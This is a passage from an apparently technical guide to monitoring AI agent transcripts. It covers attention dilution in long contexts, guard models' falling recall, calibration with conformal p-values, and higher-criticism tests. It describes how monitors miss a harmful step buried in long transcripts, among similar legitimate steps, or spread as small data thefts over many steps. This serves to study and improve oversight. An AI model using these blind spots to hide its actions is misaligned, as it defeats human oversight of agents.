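If each of the *k* harmful tokens has a logit *d* above that of the other tokens, the weight of the whole span is

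*k*·eᵈ / (*k*·eᵈ + *n* − *k*).

The span holds half the weight when eᵈ = (*n* − *k*)/*k*. For the 200 tokens of step 612, the advantage *d* must be 3.2 in a 5,000-token transcript and 7.8 in a 500,000-token transcript.

| Length in tokens | Span's share of the tokens | z-score of the average (*m* = 1) | Attention weight if *d* = 3.2 | *d* needed for half the weight |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| 5,000 | 4% | 2.8 | about 50% | 3.2 |
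| 50,000 | 0.4% | 0.89 | 9% | 5.5 |
| 500,000 | 0.04% | 0.28 | 1% | 7.8 |

Attention still gives the span 1% of the weight, 25 times what plain averaging would give it. But for a head to concentrate on step 612 as well in the full transcript as in a short excerpt, the step's logit advantage must grow with the logarithm of the length. *Let's (not) just put things in Context* (2025) also derives this requirement for the worst case. *Softmax is not Enough (for Sharp Size Generalisation)* (2024) proves that attention in a model with a finite vocabulary must eventually spread out as the text gets longer, because the logits can differ only by a limited amount.

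Replacing softmax can remove the limit. *Long-Context Generalization with Sparse Attention* (2025) analyses an alternative that can give irrelevant tokens a weight of exactly zero. If the relevant tokens score far enough above the irrelevant ones, their weight then stays the same however long the text is.

### When the other steps look similar

The 1% in the table assumes an advantage of 3.2 over every other token. In a real transcript, the advantage depends on the content of the other tokens. *The First Drop of Ink* (Gao, Chen and Huang, 2026) measured it in Llama 3.1 8B, using the few heads that find relevant passages. The passage with the answer had an advantage of about 7 to 10 over a repeated filler sentence, but only 2 to 3 over passages on the same topic that lacked the answer.

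At the midpoints of these ranges, 8.5 and 2.5, step 612 would hold 66% of the weight if the rest of the transcript were bland. Its weight would fall to 28% if ten other steps (5,000 tokens) resembled it, and to about 5% if 100 did. When an agent legitimately copies files to servers all day, a few similar steps may reduce a harmful step's weight more than hundreds of thousands of tokens of unrelated test output. *Context Poisoning as Extreme-Value Attention Interference in Long-Context Language Models* (2026) also distinguishes the raw length of a text from its effective number of distractors.

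The accuracy figures in *The First Drop of Ink* follow this pattern. At a fixed length of 128,000 tokens, Gao and colleagues gradually replaced filler with misleading passages on the question's topic. For Qwen2.5 7B on one set of questions, the first 10% of replacements caused 58% of the total loss in accuracy. Removing some misleading passages helped mainly because it shortened the text. It was clearly better than removing unrelated passages only when almost no misleading passages were left.

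### Guard models in texts of up to 32,768 words

Chen, Wu and Hu (2026), in *LongGuard*, tested how much dilution affects guard models. They took short prompts and responses with known labels from 17 safety benchmarks and hid each one in Wikipedia text. The inputs came in eight lengths, from 256 to 32,768 words, with the labelled text at the beginning, at the end or at one of three points in between. The main test used 30,400 inputs, 12,800 of them with a harmless labelled text.

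The comparison covers 13 open guard models in 15 configurations, because two models have both a strict and a loose setting. Recall fell by 50 percentage points on average between the shortest and the longest inputs. The share of harmless inputs that the models correctly passed fell by only 1.3 points.

| Guard model | Recall at 256 words | At 4,096 words | At 32,768 words |
|---|---|---|---|
| WildGuard 7B | 86% | 14% | 0.1% |
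| Llama Guard 4 12B | 56% | 9% | 7% |
| Qwen3Guard-Gen 8B (strict) | 88% | 80% | 33% |
| GuardReasoner 8B | 88% | 63% | 45% |
| GPT-OSS-SafeGuard 20B | 84% | 81% | 69% |

Formatting errors account for some of the loss. At the longest length, four of the models gave answers in the wrong format for 6.5% to 39.7% of inputs, and Chen and colleagues counted these as wrong. WildGuard had the highest rate, but formatting errors alone can't explain its fall from 86% to 0.1%.

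Recall was about 2 to 4 points higher when the Wikipedia filler was on the same topic as the hidden text than when it was random, contrary to what the calculation with similar steps would suggest. Chen and colleagues think related text keeps the model sensitive to risk. Text about a dangerous topic pushes a guard model towards the verdict "unsafe", whereas misleading passages in a question-answering test contain competing answers. Legitimate copy commands in an agent transcript could have either effect on a monitor.

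### Separating dilution from length

Either the added harmless text or the greater length itself could have caused the misses in the longer inputs. To separate the two, Chen and colleagues ran a control in which they filled the entire input with repeated copies of the harmful text. Recall fell from 85% to 68% as these inputs grew longer, compared with a fall from 76% to 25% over the same range of lengths when the filler was Wikipedia text.

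This is good evidence that dilution causes most of the loss, although the split isn't exact because repeating the harmful text also adds evidence of harm. When every token is harmful, *k* equals *n* and the averaging probe's z-score becomes *m*√*n*, which rises with length. The guard models lost 18 points despite this added evidence, so the control may understate the loss caused by length.

Researchers disagree about how much length alone matters. *Context Length Alone Hurts LLM Performance Despite Perfect Retrieval* (2025) tested five models on mathematics, question answering and coding. Their performance fell by 14% to 85% as the input grew, although they could retrieve all the relevant information. Performance fell even when the researchers masked the irrelevant tokens so that the models could attend only to the relevant ones.

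Liu argues that masking is a poor control because it leaves long gaps between token positions, which models never encounter in training. In Liu's search for a four-digit code, masking 32,000 tokens of neutral filler lowered a small model's accuracy by 46 points, while leaving the same filler visible did not lower it at all. But on multiple-choice exam questions, 4,096 tokens of visible blank space lowered the same model's accuracy from 59% to 36%. A monitor that has to reason about what it finds may therefore lose accuracy on long transcripts in ways that a simple search test does not reveal.

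### From attention to the verdict

Chen and colleagues then measured attention to the harmful text in six guard models. They took the attention from the last token of the input, where the model computes its verdict, and averaged it over all heads and layers. From the shortest to the longest inputs, this attention fell by a factor of 3.0 to 5.1. The inputs grew 128-fold, so attention to the harmful text fell far less than its share of the words.

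The model flags an input only if its output logit for the answer "unsafe" is higher than its logit for "safe". The difference between the two is the logit margin. As the filler grew, the average margin shrank in all six models, and in several the margin turned negative for many harmful inputs. When the harmful text filled the input, neither attention nor margin showed this decline. Across 48 combinations of model and length, attention, margin and recall were positively correlated even after adjusting for length, with coefficients of 0.56 to 0.83.

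In each model, the 5% of attention heads that attended most to the harmful text supplied 28% to 52% of the total attention on it. Chen and colleagues also found that the heads that favoured the harmful text over the filler at every length were mostly between 40% and 70% of the way through the layers. The general-purpose models underlying the guards already had largely the same heads, and safety training had strengthened them.

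Correlations don't establish that attention drives the verdict, so the researchers also intervened. The six models averaged 48% recall on inputs of 8,192 words or more.

- Hiding everything except the harmful text and the model's instructions raised recall to 70%.
- Showing the same amount of random filler in place of the harmful text gave 24%.
- Multiplying the selected heads' attention to the harmful text by 2, 4 and 8 raised recall by 1.5, 3.8 and 6.4 points.
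- The same change in randomly chosen heads lowered recall by 0.1 to 0.3 points.

These models flagged 24% of the inputs with no harmful text in view, so some of the 48% is probably luck rather than detection. The change to the selected heads shows that their attention affects the verdict, but even an eightfold increase recovered less than a third of the gain from hiding the filler.

### Chunked detection and attention-head sharpening

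The two repairs in *LongGuard* need no further training. Chunked detection, described earlier, splits the input into pieces of 64 to 512 words and flags the whole input if any piece looks unsafe. Attention-head sharpening leaves the input whole and divides the attention logits in the selected heads by a number below 1. Dividing by 0.5 doubles every difference between logits. In the running example, an advantage of 3.2 would become 6.4, and the span's weight would rise from 1% to 19%.

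Attention sharpening has to be selective. Gao and colleagues divided the logits by 0.9 in all heads of a question-answering model, and accuracy fell at every proportion of misleading text. They think the model's other computations depend on the attention pattern it learned in training. Chen and colleagues sharpened only 1% to 10% of the heads, and even then the strongest setting reduced performance on the shortest inputs.

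The researchers chose the best settings for each guard model, input length and text type (prompt or response). The guard first classifies the input normally, and the repair runs only if the verdict is "safe". The table gives averages for the six models on the Wikipedia test.

| Method | F1 | False positive rate | Tokens processed at 32,768 words |
|---|---|---|---|
| Original guard | 65 | 17% | 1× |
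| Chunked detection | 82 | 29% | 2.9× |
| Attention-head sharpening | 76 | 22% | 1.8× |

Across five test sets, including attacks that hide harmful requests in long prompts, chunked detection raised the main measure by an average of 22 points, and sharpening raised it by 13. The gains were mostly in models that started with low scores. PolyGuard, which already scored well, gained nothing from chunking. Sharpening requires access to the model's attention, so it works only for open models, while chunking works for any model.

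Neither repair comes close to the low false positive rates that agent monitoring requires. With 512-word chunks, the rate rose from 14% for a single chunk to 35% for 64 chunks. With 64-word chunks, it reached 75% at the longest length. The rates would probably be higher on real transcripts, which contain plenty of harmless text that a guard model would flag. The researchers had already removed every Wikipedia passage that any of a set of guard models flagged as unsafe.

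If chunks are independent, the rise from 14% to 35% corresponds to a false positive rate of about 0.44% for each extra chunk. If a company scored each of the 1,000 steps in the running example separately, with that same false positive rate per step, about 99% of clean transcripts would get at least one false flag. Chunking therefore needs a much stricter threshold than the one the guard models ordinarily use to label text "safe" or "unsafe".

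### Why attention weight does not prove influence

A span with a low attention weight can still affect the result. The head multiplies each weight by a value vector, so a span with 1% of the weight can decide the result if the contributions from the other 99% largely cancel out. Information from step 612 can also reach the final token indirectly, because the tokens just after that step can take up its content and the final token can then attend to them.

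A high weight can be equally misleading, because the tokens that receive it may contain nothing important. Many attention heads put their weight on the first few tokens of the input when they detect nothing relevant, a pattern called an attention sink. In one 4,096-token agent transcript in *FocuSFT* (2026), only 13.5% of the attention from the model's responses went to the content of the context.

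In *Can Language Models Actually Retrieve In-Context?*, Gollapudi, Gupta and colleagues (2026) used a better measure, which includes the value vectors. They trained a small language model to find which document in its context answers a question. As the number of documents grew from 500 to 10,000, or about a million tokens, the right document's share of one layer's output fell from 0.91 to 0.01. The total output shrank by only about a third, so other documents had replaced the right one.

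Some attention heads still ranked the right document first when the model answered incorrectly. With 5,000 documents, at least one head in that layer did so for 33% of questions, while the model gave the right answer for 19%. The researchers then multiplied the attention logits by a factor that grows with the logarithm of the collection's size, a correction that follows from the softmax formula. At 10,000 documents, this raised accuracy from 0.2% to about 17%, close to the 20% of a conventional search model. Even then, the right document received less than 2% of the layer's attention, so a weight that small can be enough for a correct answer.

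In 126,473 trials on five small models, Liu found that attention on the evidence explained 35% to 58% of the variation in loss (a measure of how low a probability the model gave the right answer), compared with 2% to 8% for the logarithm of length. But Liu did not alter the attention, so these figures don't establish that it affected the loss. To establish that a passage influenced a verdict, an investigator has to change or remove the passage and check whether the verdict changes. Several methods in the section on finding the decisive step do this.

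### From guard models to monitors of agents

The running example is far outside the range that Chen and colleagues tested. Its transcript is more than ten times as long as their longest inputs, which had roughly 40,000 tokens, and step 612 makes up only 0.04% of it. In their most diluted group, the harmful text made up less than 0.5% of the words, and recall was 32% for prompts and 34% for responses.

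The hidden texts also differed from harmful steps in agent transcripts. A request for help with a crime stands out more in an encyclopedia article than a harmful command does among hundreds of other commands. In a smaller test with computer code as filler, the recall of the six guard models fell from 84% to 49%, so the problem isn't specific to Wikipedia. But the hidden texts in that test came from the same chat benchmarks.

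Large, general-purpose models can have this problem too. Gollapudi and colleagues gave their document task to Gemini 3 Flash, a general-purpose model with a long context window, and its accuracy fell from 95% with 500 documents to 16% with 10,000. The collection contained many near-misses chosen to be confusing, so an ordinary coding session may be easier.

A monitor that reasons before answering has more than one chance to find the evidence. If it writes "check whether any file left the company", the queries for its next tokens may match step 612 much better than the original instruction did, which raises *d*. But *Let's (not) just put things in Context* proves that extra reasoning tokens can't recover the evidence unless at least one of them attends to it substantially. The results for guard models that write out their reasoning are consistent with both points: GPT-OSS-SafeGuard lost only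 15 points of recall, while GuardReasoner lost 44 and Nemotron Reasoning lost 63. The study of attention didn't cover any of these three models, so it offers no direct evidence about how reasoning changes dilution.

Dilution also can't explain every failure on agent transcripts. It predicts that a long harmful transcript will look more like a clean one. But in the payment tests by Yang and colleagues, the scores of long clean transcripts rose, which must have some other cause.

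Both formulas also leave out position. In *LongGuard*, recall for prompts was higher at the edges than in the middle, by 7 points at 256 words and by 31 points at 16,384 words. The frontier monitors that missed obvious commands inside long transcripts could identify them when the transcript ended right after the command. If *d* stayed at 3.2, cutting everything after step 612 would leave 305,000 tokens before it and raise its attention weight only from 1.0% to 1.6%. The monitors' improvement is large for such a small change in weight, which suggests that *d* itself depends on position. *FocuSFT* describes such a bias, in which tokens near the beginning and end of a text get more attention regardless of their relevance.

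## Calibrating scores on clean transcripts

A monitor built by prompting a language model generates its scores as it generates any other text, so a score of 0.9 doesn't necessarily mean that 90% of such steps are harmful. In *ConformalGuard*, Bista, Jadhav and colleagues (2026) asked two general-purpose models for the probability that an email was phishing. Across thousands of emails, Claude Sonnet 4 used only 11 different values and GPT-4o only 10, and neither gave a number between 0.3 and 0.7.

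Like precision, a calibrated probability is accurate only at the base rate of the data used to calibrate it. If a score of 0.9 means a 90% chance of harm in a test set that is half harmful, the same score means only a 0.9% chance at a base rate of 0.1%.

### Ranking a score among clean ones

A p-value doesn't depend on the base rate, because a team can calculate it from clean data alone. The team runs the monitor on N clean cases, called the calibration set, and ranks each new score among theirs:

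p = (1 + number of clean scores at least as high) / (N + 1).

Statisticians call this a conformal p-value. *Testing for Outliers with Conformal p-values* (Bates, Candès and colleagues, 2021) analyses its use for finding unusual cases. In the earlier example, 30 of 10,000 clean steps scored 7 or higher, so a score of 7 has a p-value of 31/10,001, or 0.0031. The 1 added to both numbers counts the new case itself. It barely changes the result here, but with only 99 calibration scores, a new score above all of them gets a p-value of 1/100 instead of an implausible zero.

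To see why the formula works, suppose the new case is clean and no scores tie. The new score is then equally likely to hold any of the N + 1 ranks, so its chance of being the highest is 1/(N + 1). A p-value of 0.01 or less therefore occurs in at most 1% of clean cases. This holds no matter how well the monitor detects harm.

The argument assumes that a new clean transcript and the calibration transcripts are exchangeable, meaning that their scores are equally likely to occur in any order. No one could then do better than chance at picking out the new transcript by its score. The team also has to fix the monitor's model and prompt before calibrating, and it can't calibrate on transcripts it used to choose the prompt. If an engineer has adjusted the prompt until certain transcripts no longer trigger flags, those transcripts will tend to score lower than new ones.

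In the email test, Bista and colleagues first set thresholds the usual way, tuning them on labelled examples for a 1% false positive rate. With Claude's scores, the actual rate on new emails was 4.0%. Conformal p-values computed from 2,000 legitimate emails reduced it to 0.8%, but recall fell from 94% to 88%. The ranking of the emails didn't change, so both differences came entirely from the choice of threshold.

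### How far off one calibration set can be

The 1% is an average over all the calibration sets that a team might have collected, but the team has only one. Bates and colleagues give the distribution of the actual false positive rate from one set to another. For a target rate α and scores without ties, it is

Beta(ℓ, N + 1 − ℓ), where ℓ is (N + 1)α rounded down.

With 99 clean transcripts and a target of 1%, the false-flag rate follows a Beta(1, 99) distribution. Its mean is 1%, but 37% of calibration sets would give a higher rate, and about 5% would give a rate above 3%. At the company with 10,000 transcripts a day, a 3% rate means about 300 false flags a day instead of 100 until the team recalibrates. With 9,999 clean transcripts, the rate would typically be within 0.1 percentage points of the target.

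To be 95% confident that the false-alarm rate is no higher than α, a team can again use the 3/*n* rule from the length tests. Gao (2026), in *From Probe Scores to Alarm Policies*, gives the exact minimum as log(0.05)/log(1 − α) independent clean cases, which rounds up to 59 for a rate of 5% and 299 for 1%. With only the minimum number of cases, the monitor may flag only scores above the highest clean score. One of Gao's test sets had 23 clean cases for calibration, too few to support even a 10% rate, so Gao set no threshold for it.

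### One transcript with 1,000 steps

The smallest p-value that N clean cases can produce is 1/(N + 1). This limit matters when a monitor scores every step. Dividing a 1% false positive rate equally among a transcript's 1,000 steps (see the section on setting thresholds) leaves 0.00001 per step. A p-value that small requires about 100,000 clean steps, or 100 transcripts of that length.

Alternatively, the team can take the highest step score in each transcript and rank it against the highest step score from each clean transcript.

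| | Ranking each step | Ranking the highest score |
|---|---|---|
| p-value needed for a 1% rate | 0.00001 | 0.01 |
| Minimum clean data | 99,999 steps (100 transcripts) | 99 transcripts |
| What has to be exchangeable | Steps | Transcripts |
| Result | A p-value for every step | One p-value for the transcript |

At these minimum sizes, both methods use almost the same data and give almost the same threshold, because the highest score among all steps is also the highest of the transcripts' maximum scores. But ranking each transcript's maximum score is safer because it works however the steps within a transcript depend on each other.

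Suppose the 100,000 clean steps come from only ten very long sessions, and scores depend mainly on the kind of work in a session. A new clean session then has about a 1 in 11 chance of outscoring all ten, so the real false positive rate is about 9% rather than the 1% implied by the step count. Ranking sessions by their highest scores makes the shortage of sessions obvious, since ten sessions can't produce a p-value below 1/11.

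Dependence can also make the step method too strict. With 1,000 clean transcripts of 1,000 steps each, the monitor would flag any step that scores above the tenth-highest clean step. If the ten highest-scoring steps all come from one transcript in which the agent kept retrying an odd command, the monitor will flag only about 0.1% of clean transcripts and miss harmful ones that a 1% rate would have caught.

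Ranking only the highest score loses the p-values for individual steps. A reviewer can still start with the highest-scoring step, but three moderately suspicious payments count no more than the most suspicious one alone. With either this method or the step method, a harmful step has to stand out from the highest clean scores. If 0.3% of clean steps score 7 or more and steps are independent, 95% of clean 1,000-step transcripts contain at least one such step. A score of 7 for step 612 then has a p-value of 0.003 among steps, but if it is the highest score in a 1,000-step transcript, the transcript's p-value is about 0.95.

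Gao's results on AgentDojo show how large this loss can be. One probe had an AUROC of 0.92 when Gao judged each of an agent's attempts separately. Gao then took the highest score over ten attempts at each task and calibrated the threshold for a 5% false positive rate. At that threshold, the probe detected none of the 38 tasks in which an attack succeeded.

In *Online Safety Monitoring for LLMs*, Schirmer, Jazbec and colleagues (2026) used an equivalent method, using whole safe sequences to calibrate one threshold for all steps. False alarms stayed within the target in tests on mathematical solutions and on conversations in which people tried to provoke harmful answers. However, the calibration and test data came from the same datasets, so exchangeability is much more likely there than in a company's changing traffic.

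### Checking the calibration

A team can check its calibration with new clean transcripts. About 1% of them should have a p-value of 0.01 or less, and about 5% a p-value of 0.05 or less. *Data-quality monitoring of luminosity blocks with ATLAS Open Data* (2026) applies the same check to short stretches of data from a particle detector. Because its calibration and test data are weeks apart, it treats exchangeability as an assumption and measures the false positive rate on the later clean data. If the check fails, the pattern of errors often points to the cause.

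### Scores that drift with length or position

If most false flags come from long transcripts, the calibration set probably mixes lengths. Suppose 90% of clean transcripts have 15 steps and 10% have 1,000, and each step has the same independent chance of a false flag. A threshold that flags 1% of clean transcripts overall then flags about 0.14% of the short ones and 8.8% of the long ones.

The gap widens if clean text scores higher in long transcripts, as Yang and colleagues found in their payment tests. If it scores lower, the team will see fewer low p-values than expected among long clean transcripts, and the monitor will miss more of the harmful long transcripts.

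The remedy is to rank each transcript only among clean ones of similar length. *GridAnchor* (2026), which describes a system for checking AI agents that manage energy supplies, applies the same idea to types of claim. Its scores are distributed differently for each type, so it calculates p-values within six classes. Each group needs its own calibration data, so using five length bands at the 1% level would take at least 495 clean transcripts instead of 99.

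Schirmer and colleagues point out that scores may also depend on a step's position, which a single threshold ignores. If clean scores rise towards the end of a transcript, the highest score usually comes from a late step. Matching by length keeps the false positive rate correct, but step 612 still has to outscore clean steps near the end. To avoid this, the team can compute a p-value for each step by ranking it among clean steps at similar positions, then use the smallest p-value as the transcript's score. It then ranks that score among the scores of clean transcripts, computed the same way.

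### A new agent model or mix of tasks

A sudden change in the number of flags after a release suggests that the calibration set no longer represents the traffic. In Gao's AgentDojo test, thresholds meant to keep the false positive rate below 10% produced rates of 19% to 20%. Gao calculated that one of these monitors would produce so many false positives less than 0.2% of the time if the calibration and test cases had the same distribution. The two sets contained different user tasks, which may explain the mismatch.

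Bista and colleagues found smaller errors when they calibrated on legitimate emails from one collection and tested on another. With a target false positive rate of 1%, the highest actual rate was 2.1%, for a small classifier they trained themselves. Claude's rate stayed below 1% whichever collection they used for calibration.

A small change in the mix of clean sessions can raise the false positive rate only by a limited amount. For example, if 2% of clean sessions are of a kind that the calibration set lacks, and nothing else has changed, the expected false positive rate can rise from 1% to at most about 3%. But if a new agent model writes differently in every session, the old calibration gives no useful limit on the false positive rate.

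Bista and colleagues recommend collecting and scoring a fresh calibration set after any change to the monitor's model or prompt. A fresh set is also needed when the agent changes, and each new set has to include every kind of work the agents do. *ConfGuard* (2026), which covers monitors for AI agents that maintain machinery, kept the false alarm rate between 2.1% and 3.4%, under a limit of 5%, when the calibration machines and the monitored machines were drawn in the same way.

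### Harmful cases in the "clean" set

A team that samples its own traffic will sometimes pick up harmful transcripts by accident. At a base rate of 0.1%, a random sample of 299 transcripts has a 26% chance of containing at least one. If a harmful transcript has the highest score in the sample, it raises the threshold, and later harmful transcripts have to outscore it to be flagged. The monitor then misses more harm and produces fewer false flags than intended, so reviewers are unlikely to notice the problem.

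*Robust Conformal Outlier Detection under Contaminated Reference Data* (Bashari, Sesia and Romano, 2025) measured this effect on six sets of images with a target false positive rate of 1%. It compared three ways of treating the contaminated set: leaving it alone, deleting its highest-scoring cases without checking them, and checking the 50 highest-scoring cases and removing only the real outliers.

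| Outliers in the "clean" set | False positive rate if left alone | After blind deletion | After checking 50 cases | Relative gain in recall from checking |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| 1% | 0.8% | 1.7% | 1.0% | 17% |
| 3% | 0.5% | 2.7% | 1.0% | 52% |
| 5% | 0.4% | 3.6% | 0.8% | 79% |

Deleting the highest-scoring cases without checking them also removes clean cases that happen to score high, which lowers the threshold too far. For transcripts, a person can fix this by reading the highest-scoring ones in the calibration set and removing only those with confirmed harm.

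Language models are a risky substitute for that person. When Xu asked two frontier models to check an early version of a benchmark for data leaks, both approved all 40 scenarios. A simple count then showed that the leaked value was the larger or later one in 25 of 28 comparable pairs, which gave monitors an unintended clue. A model that removes harmless but odd-looking transcripts from a calibration set would cause the same problem as blind deletion.

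### Yes/no answers and tied scores

If a monitor outputs only "true" or "false" and wrongly flags 2% of clean transcripts, it can produce just two p-values, about 0.02 for "true" and 1 for "false". Any threshold that keeps its false positive rate at or below 1% will therefore flag nothing.

Coarse numerical scores cause a milder version of this problem. The formula counts every tied clean score against the new case, so ties raise the p-value and lower recall. With GPT-4o's ten values, Bista and colleagues got a recall of 56% and a false positive rate of 0.1% at every target they tried from 0.1% to 1%. At a target of 5%, recall was 89% and the false positive rate was 1.5%. A false positive rate that stays the same when the target changes is a sign of ties. Ranking transcripts by their highest step score makes ties more common, because many long clean transcripts will share a highest score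 of 8 or 9 out of 10.

Rescaling the scores doesn't help, because two cases with the same score still have the same score afterwards. The monitor has to produce finer scores:

- **Probabilities of the answer.** Some models provide the probability of each possible next word. Schirmer and colleagues used the probability that Llama Guard gave to "safe" instead of its verdict.
- **Averages of several runs.** With some randomness in GPT-4o's answers, averaging three runs instead of using one raised recall from 29% to 73%, while the false positive rate stayed at about 0.5%. This triples the cost of monitoring.
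- **Random tie-breaking.** This raised GPT-4o's recall to 80% with a false positive rate of 1.1%, but 17% of the decisions then depended on a random number. Reviewers would find it hard to explain why the monitor flagged one transcript and not another with the same score.

### Many steps from few transcripts

When a calibration set has many steps from few sessions, false flags tend to cluster, and leaving out a single session can move the threshold noticeably. A team that needs p-values for individual steps should sample from as many transcripts as possible. Taking 100 steps from each of 1,000 transcripts yields as many steps as taking all 1,000 steps from each of 100 transcripts, but covers ten times as many sessions.

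Error estimates also have to treat each transcript as one unit, because scores from the same transcript are correlated. The ATLAS study had similar correlations between blocks from one run of the detector, so it estimated its uncertainty by drawing whole runs at random with replacement 1,000 times and recalculating the results each time. A team can do the same with whole transcripts.

### Extrapolating beyond the highest clean score

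A company that wants a false positive rate of 0.01% needs at least 9,999 clean transcripts of the right length. If it has only a few hundred, it can fit a curve, called a tail model, to the highest scores and extend it beyond them. The extension depends on which curve the company chooses, and it can't tell from its data whether that choice is right.

Suppose 10% of clean transcripts have a highest score above 5, and 1% have one above 6, on a scale with no upper limit. Three common curves match both figures exactly but disagree about a score of 8:

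| Shape of the tail | Share of clean transcripts above 8 |
|---|---|
| Normal distribution | 0.0005% |
| Exponential | 0.01% |
| Power law | 0.026% |

The highest estimate is about 50 times the lowest. Real scores may follow none of these curves, for instance if a rare kind of session produces most of the extreme values. A wrong null model later caused serious problems in brain imaging, as the section on spans describes. Gao avoids extrapolation and sets no threshold when there are too few clean cases. A team can test a tail model on held-out clean transcripts, but confirming a rate of 0.01% takes about 30,000 of them with no false flags.

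## Combining the scores of many steps into one test

Calibration gives each step a p-value, but a team must then combine a thousand p-values into one decision about the transcript. Using only the smallest p-value ignores any other steps that look moderately suspicious. Averaging the scores includes every step but dilutes the signal from a single harmful one. The best method depends on how many steps are harmful, how much their scores differ from those of harmless steps, and whether the harmful steps are consecutive.

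### A model with a few shifted scores

Statisticians study this problem with the sparse mixture model. A transcript has *n* independent scores, scaled so that clean ones follow a normal distribution with mean 0 and standard deviation 1. In a harmful transcript, a few scores are higher by an amount μ. Two numbers, *b* and *r*, describe how few and how much higher:

number of harmful steps = *n*^(1 − *b*)

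μ = √(2*r* ln *n*).

With 10,000 steps, *b* = 1/2 means 100 harmful steps, *b* = 3/4 means 10, and *b* = 1 means one. The highest of *n* clean scores is roughly √(2 ln *n*), so at *r* = 1 a typical harmful step scores about as high as the highest clean one.

Donoho and Jin (2004), in *Higher Criticism for Detecting Sparse Heterogeneous Mixtures*, give the smallest *r* that any test can detect, building on earlier results by Ingster. This detection boundary is

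*r* = *b* − 1/2, for *b* between 1/2 and 3/4

*r* = (1 − √(1 − *b*))², for *b* above 3/4.

As *n* grows, the best test's false positive rate and miss rate both approach zero above the boundary, while every test approaches random guessing below it. These asymptotic results describe ever longer transcripts and can be far off at realistic lengths.

### The price of length for one harmful step

For a single harmful step, the boundary is *r* = 1, or a shift of √(2 ln *n*). That is about 3.7 standard deviations among 1,000 steps and 5.3 among a million, so a thousand times as many steps raises the requirement by only about 1.5.

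A step exactly at the boundary would still be missed most of the time. With 1,000 steps, a 1% false positive rate for the whole transcript requires a threshold of 4.3, and a step shifted by 3.7 reaches it only 29% of the time. The table gives the shift needed for 90% recall at that false positive rate.

| Steps | Boundary | Shift needed, using the highest score | Shift needed, using the average |
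|---|---|---|---|
| 15 | 2.3 | 4.5 | 14 |
| 1,000 | 3.7 | 5.5 | 114 |
| 10,000 | 4.3 | 6.0 | 361 |
| 1,000,000 | 5.3 | 6.9 | 3,608 |

When the test uses the highest step score, a slightly better monitor makes up for the purely statistical effect of a much longer transcript. If the monitor does not improve, however, recall falls as the transcript grows. The same shift in a harmful step's score that gives 90% recall at 15 steps gives 59% at 1,000.

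In tests by Martin and Roger, one monitor detected only 5% of harmful actions after they added 600,000 tokens of clean activity, or about 1,200 steps at 500 tokens each. By the arithmetic above, if extra comparisons were the only cause of this low recall, the monitor would have had 29% recall at 15 steps. If it did much better than that on the original short transcripts, it must have become worse at assessing the harmful step itself.

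### Higher criticism

When several steps are moderately suspicious, a team can count them and compare the count with what chance would produce. Donoho and Jin trace this idea to the statistician John Tukey, who told his students about a psychologist proud of 11 significant results. The psychologist had run 250 tests at the 5% level, so chance alone would have produced about 12.5 on average.

Tukey's version used one fixed cut-off. The higher criticism statistic tries many and keeps the most surprising count. The team sorts the p-values from smallest to largest, writes *p*₍ᵢ₎ for the *i*-th smallest, and calculates

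HC = max over *i* of (*i* − *n*·*p*₍ᵢ₎) / √(*n*·*p*₍ᵢ₎(1 − *p*₍ᵢ₎)).

The top of the fraction is the number of steps with p-values at or below *p*₍ᵢ₎, minus the number expected by chance. The bottom is the standard deviation of that count. The search usually covers at most the smaller half of the p-values.

Suppose a transcript has 100 steps, and the eight smallest p-values lie between 0.006 and 0.020. The ninth is 0.090.

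| Rank | p-value | Steps expected by chance | Surplus | Surplus in standard deviations |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | 0.006 | 0.6 | 0.4 | 0.5 |
| 4 | 0.013 | 1.3 | 2.7 | 2.4 |
| 8 | 0.020 | 2.0 | 6.0 | 4.3 |
| 9 | 0.090 | 9.0 | 0.0 | 0.0 |

The higher criticism statistic is 4.3, based on the eight steps with p-values at or below 0.020. Only about 0.1% of clean transcripts would have that many. The highest score alone gives no reason for suspicion, because 45% of clean transcripts of this length contain a p-value of 0.006 or less. The 0.1% figure is too low, however, because higher criticism picks the most striking of many cut-offs. A team should therefore compute the same statistic for whole clean transcripts and see where 4.3 ranks among the results.

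One tiny p-value can also dominate the result. In a transcript of 100 steps, a p-value of 0.0001 produces a test statistic of 9.9 by itself, and about 1% of clean transcripts contain a p-value that small. Donoho and Jin therefore suggest a version that ignores p-values below 1/*n*, which in their experience worked better with moderate samples. This version ignores a single extreme step, so a team using it also needs to check the highest score.

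In theory, higher criticism reaches the detection boundary without requiring the values of *b* or *r*, while the highest score reaches it only when *b* is at least 3/4. Higher criticism therefore has an advantage when the number of harmful steps is between the fourth root and the square root of *n*, or roughly 6 to 32 steps among 1,000 and 10 to 100 among 10,000. It has no advantage for the single harmful step in the running example. Fisher's method, an older technique that adds the logarithms of all the p-values, fails throughout this range because the many clean steps swamp the few harmful ones.

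### Forty weak steps among 10,000

An agent that steals data in small pieces might leave 40 weakly suspicious steps among 10,000. Here *b* is about 0.6, so the boundary is *r* = 0.1, which corresponds to a shift of about 1.4 standard deviations. In theory, a test that uses only the highest score needs a shift of about 1.6 standard deviations.

At this length, however, no test works well at a shift of 1.4. The table compares three simple tests, each with a false positive rate of 1%. The third, which is higher criticism with a single cut-off, flags a transcript if at least seven steps score above 3.5.

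| Shift of the 40 steps | Recall of the average | Recall of the highest score | Recall of the count above 3.5 |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1.4 | 4% | 3% | 3% |
| 2.0 | 6% | 12% | 23% |
| 2.5 | 9% | 39% | 78% |
| 3.0 | 13% | 81% | over 99% |

The count does much better once the shift is at least 2, which supports the idea behind higher criticism. Full higher criticism loses some power because it tries many cut-offs, but the team doesn't have to guess the right one beforehand.

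Donoho and Jin's own calculations show how slowly detection approaches its theoretical limit. With *b* = 1/2 and *r* = 0.05, harm is detectable in the limit as the number of scores grows. But with ten billion scores, the expected surplus at the theoretically best cut-off is 2.3 standard deviations, below the approximate critical value of 2.5. A team should therefore use the boundary to choose between statistics, but estimate recall by simulating or planting harmful steps.

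Assuming equal shifts is another simplification. In *Optimal Detection For Sparse Mixtures*, Cai and Wu (2014) extend the theory to harmful scores that vary in strength and find that higher criticism remains optimal under fairly broad conditions. They also cite a formula for harmful scores that vary more than clean ones. If the harmful scores have a variance of 1.5 instead of 1, the boundary for the 40 steps falls from 1.4 to about 1.0, because some harmful steps then score well above the others.

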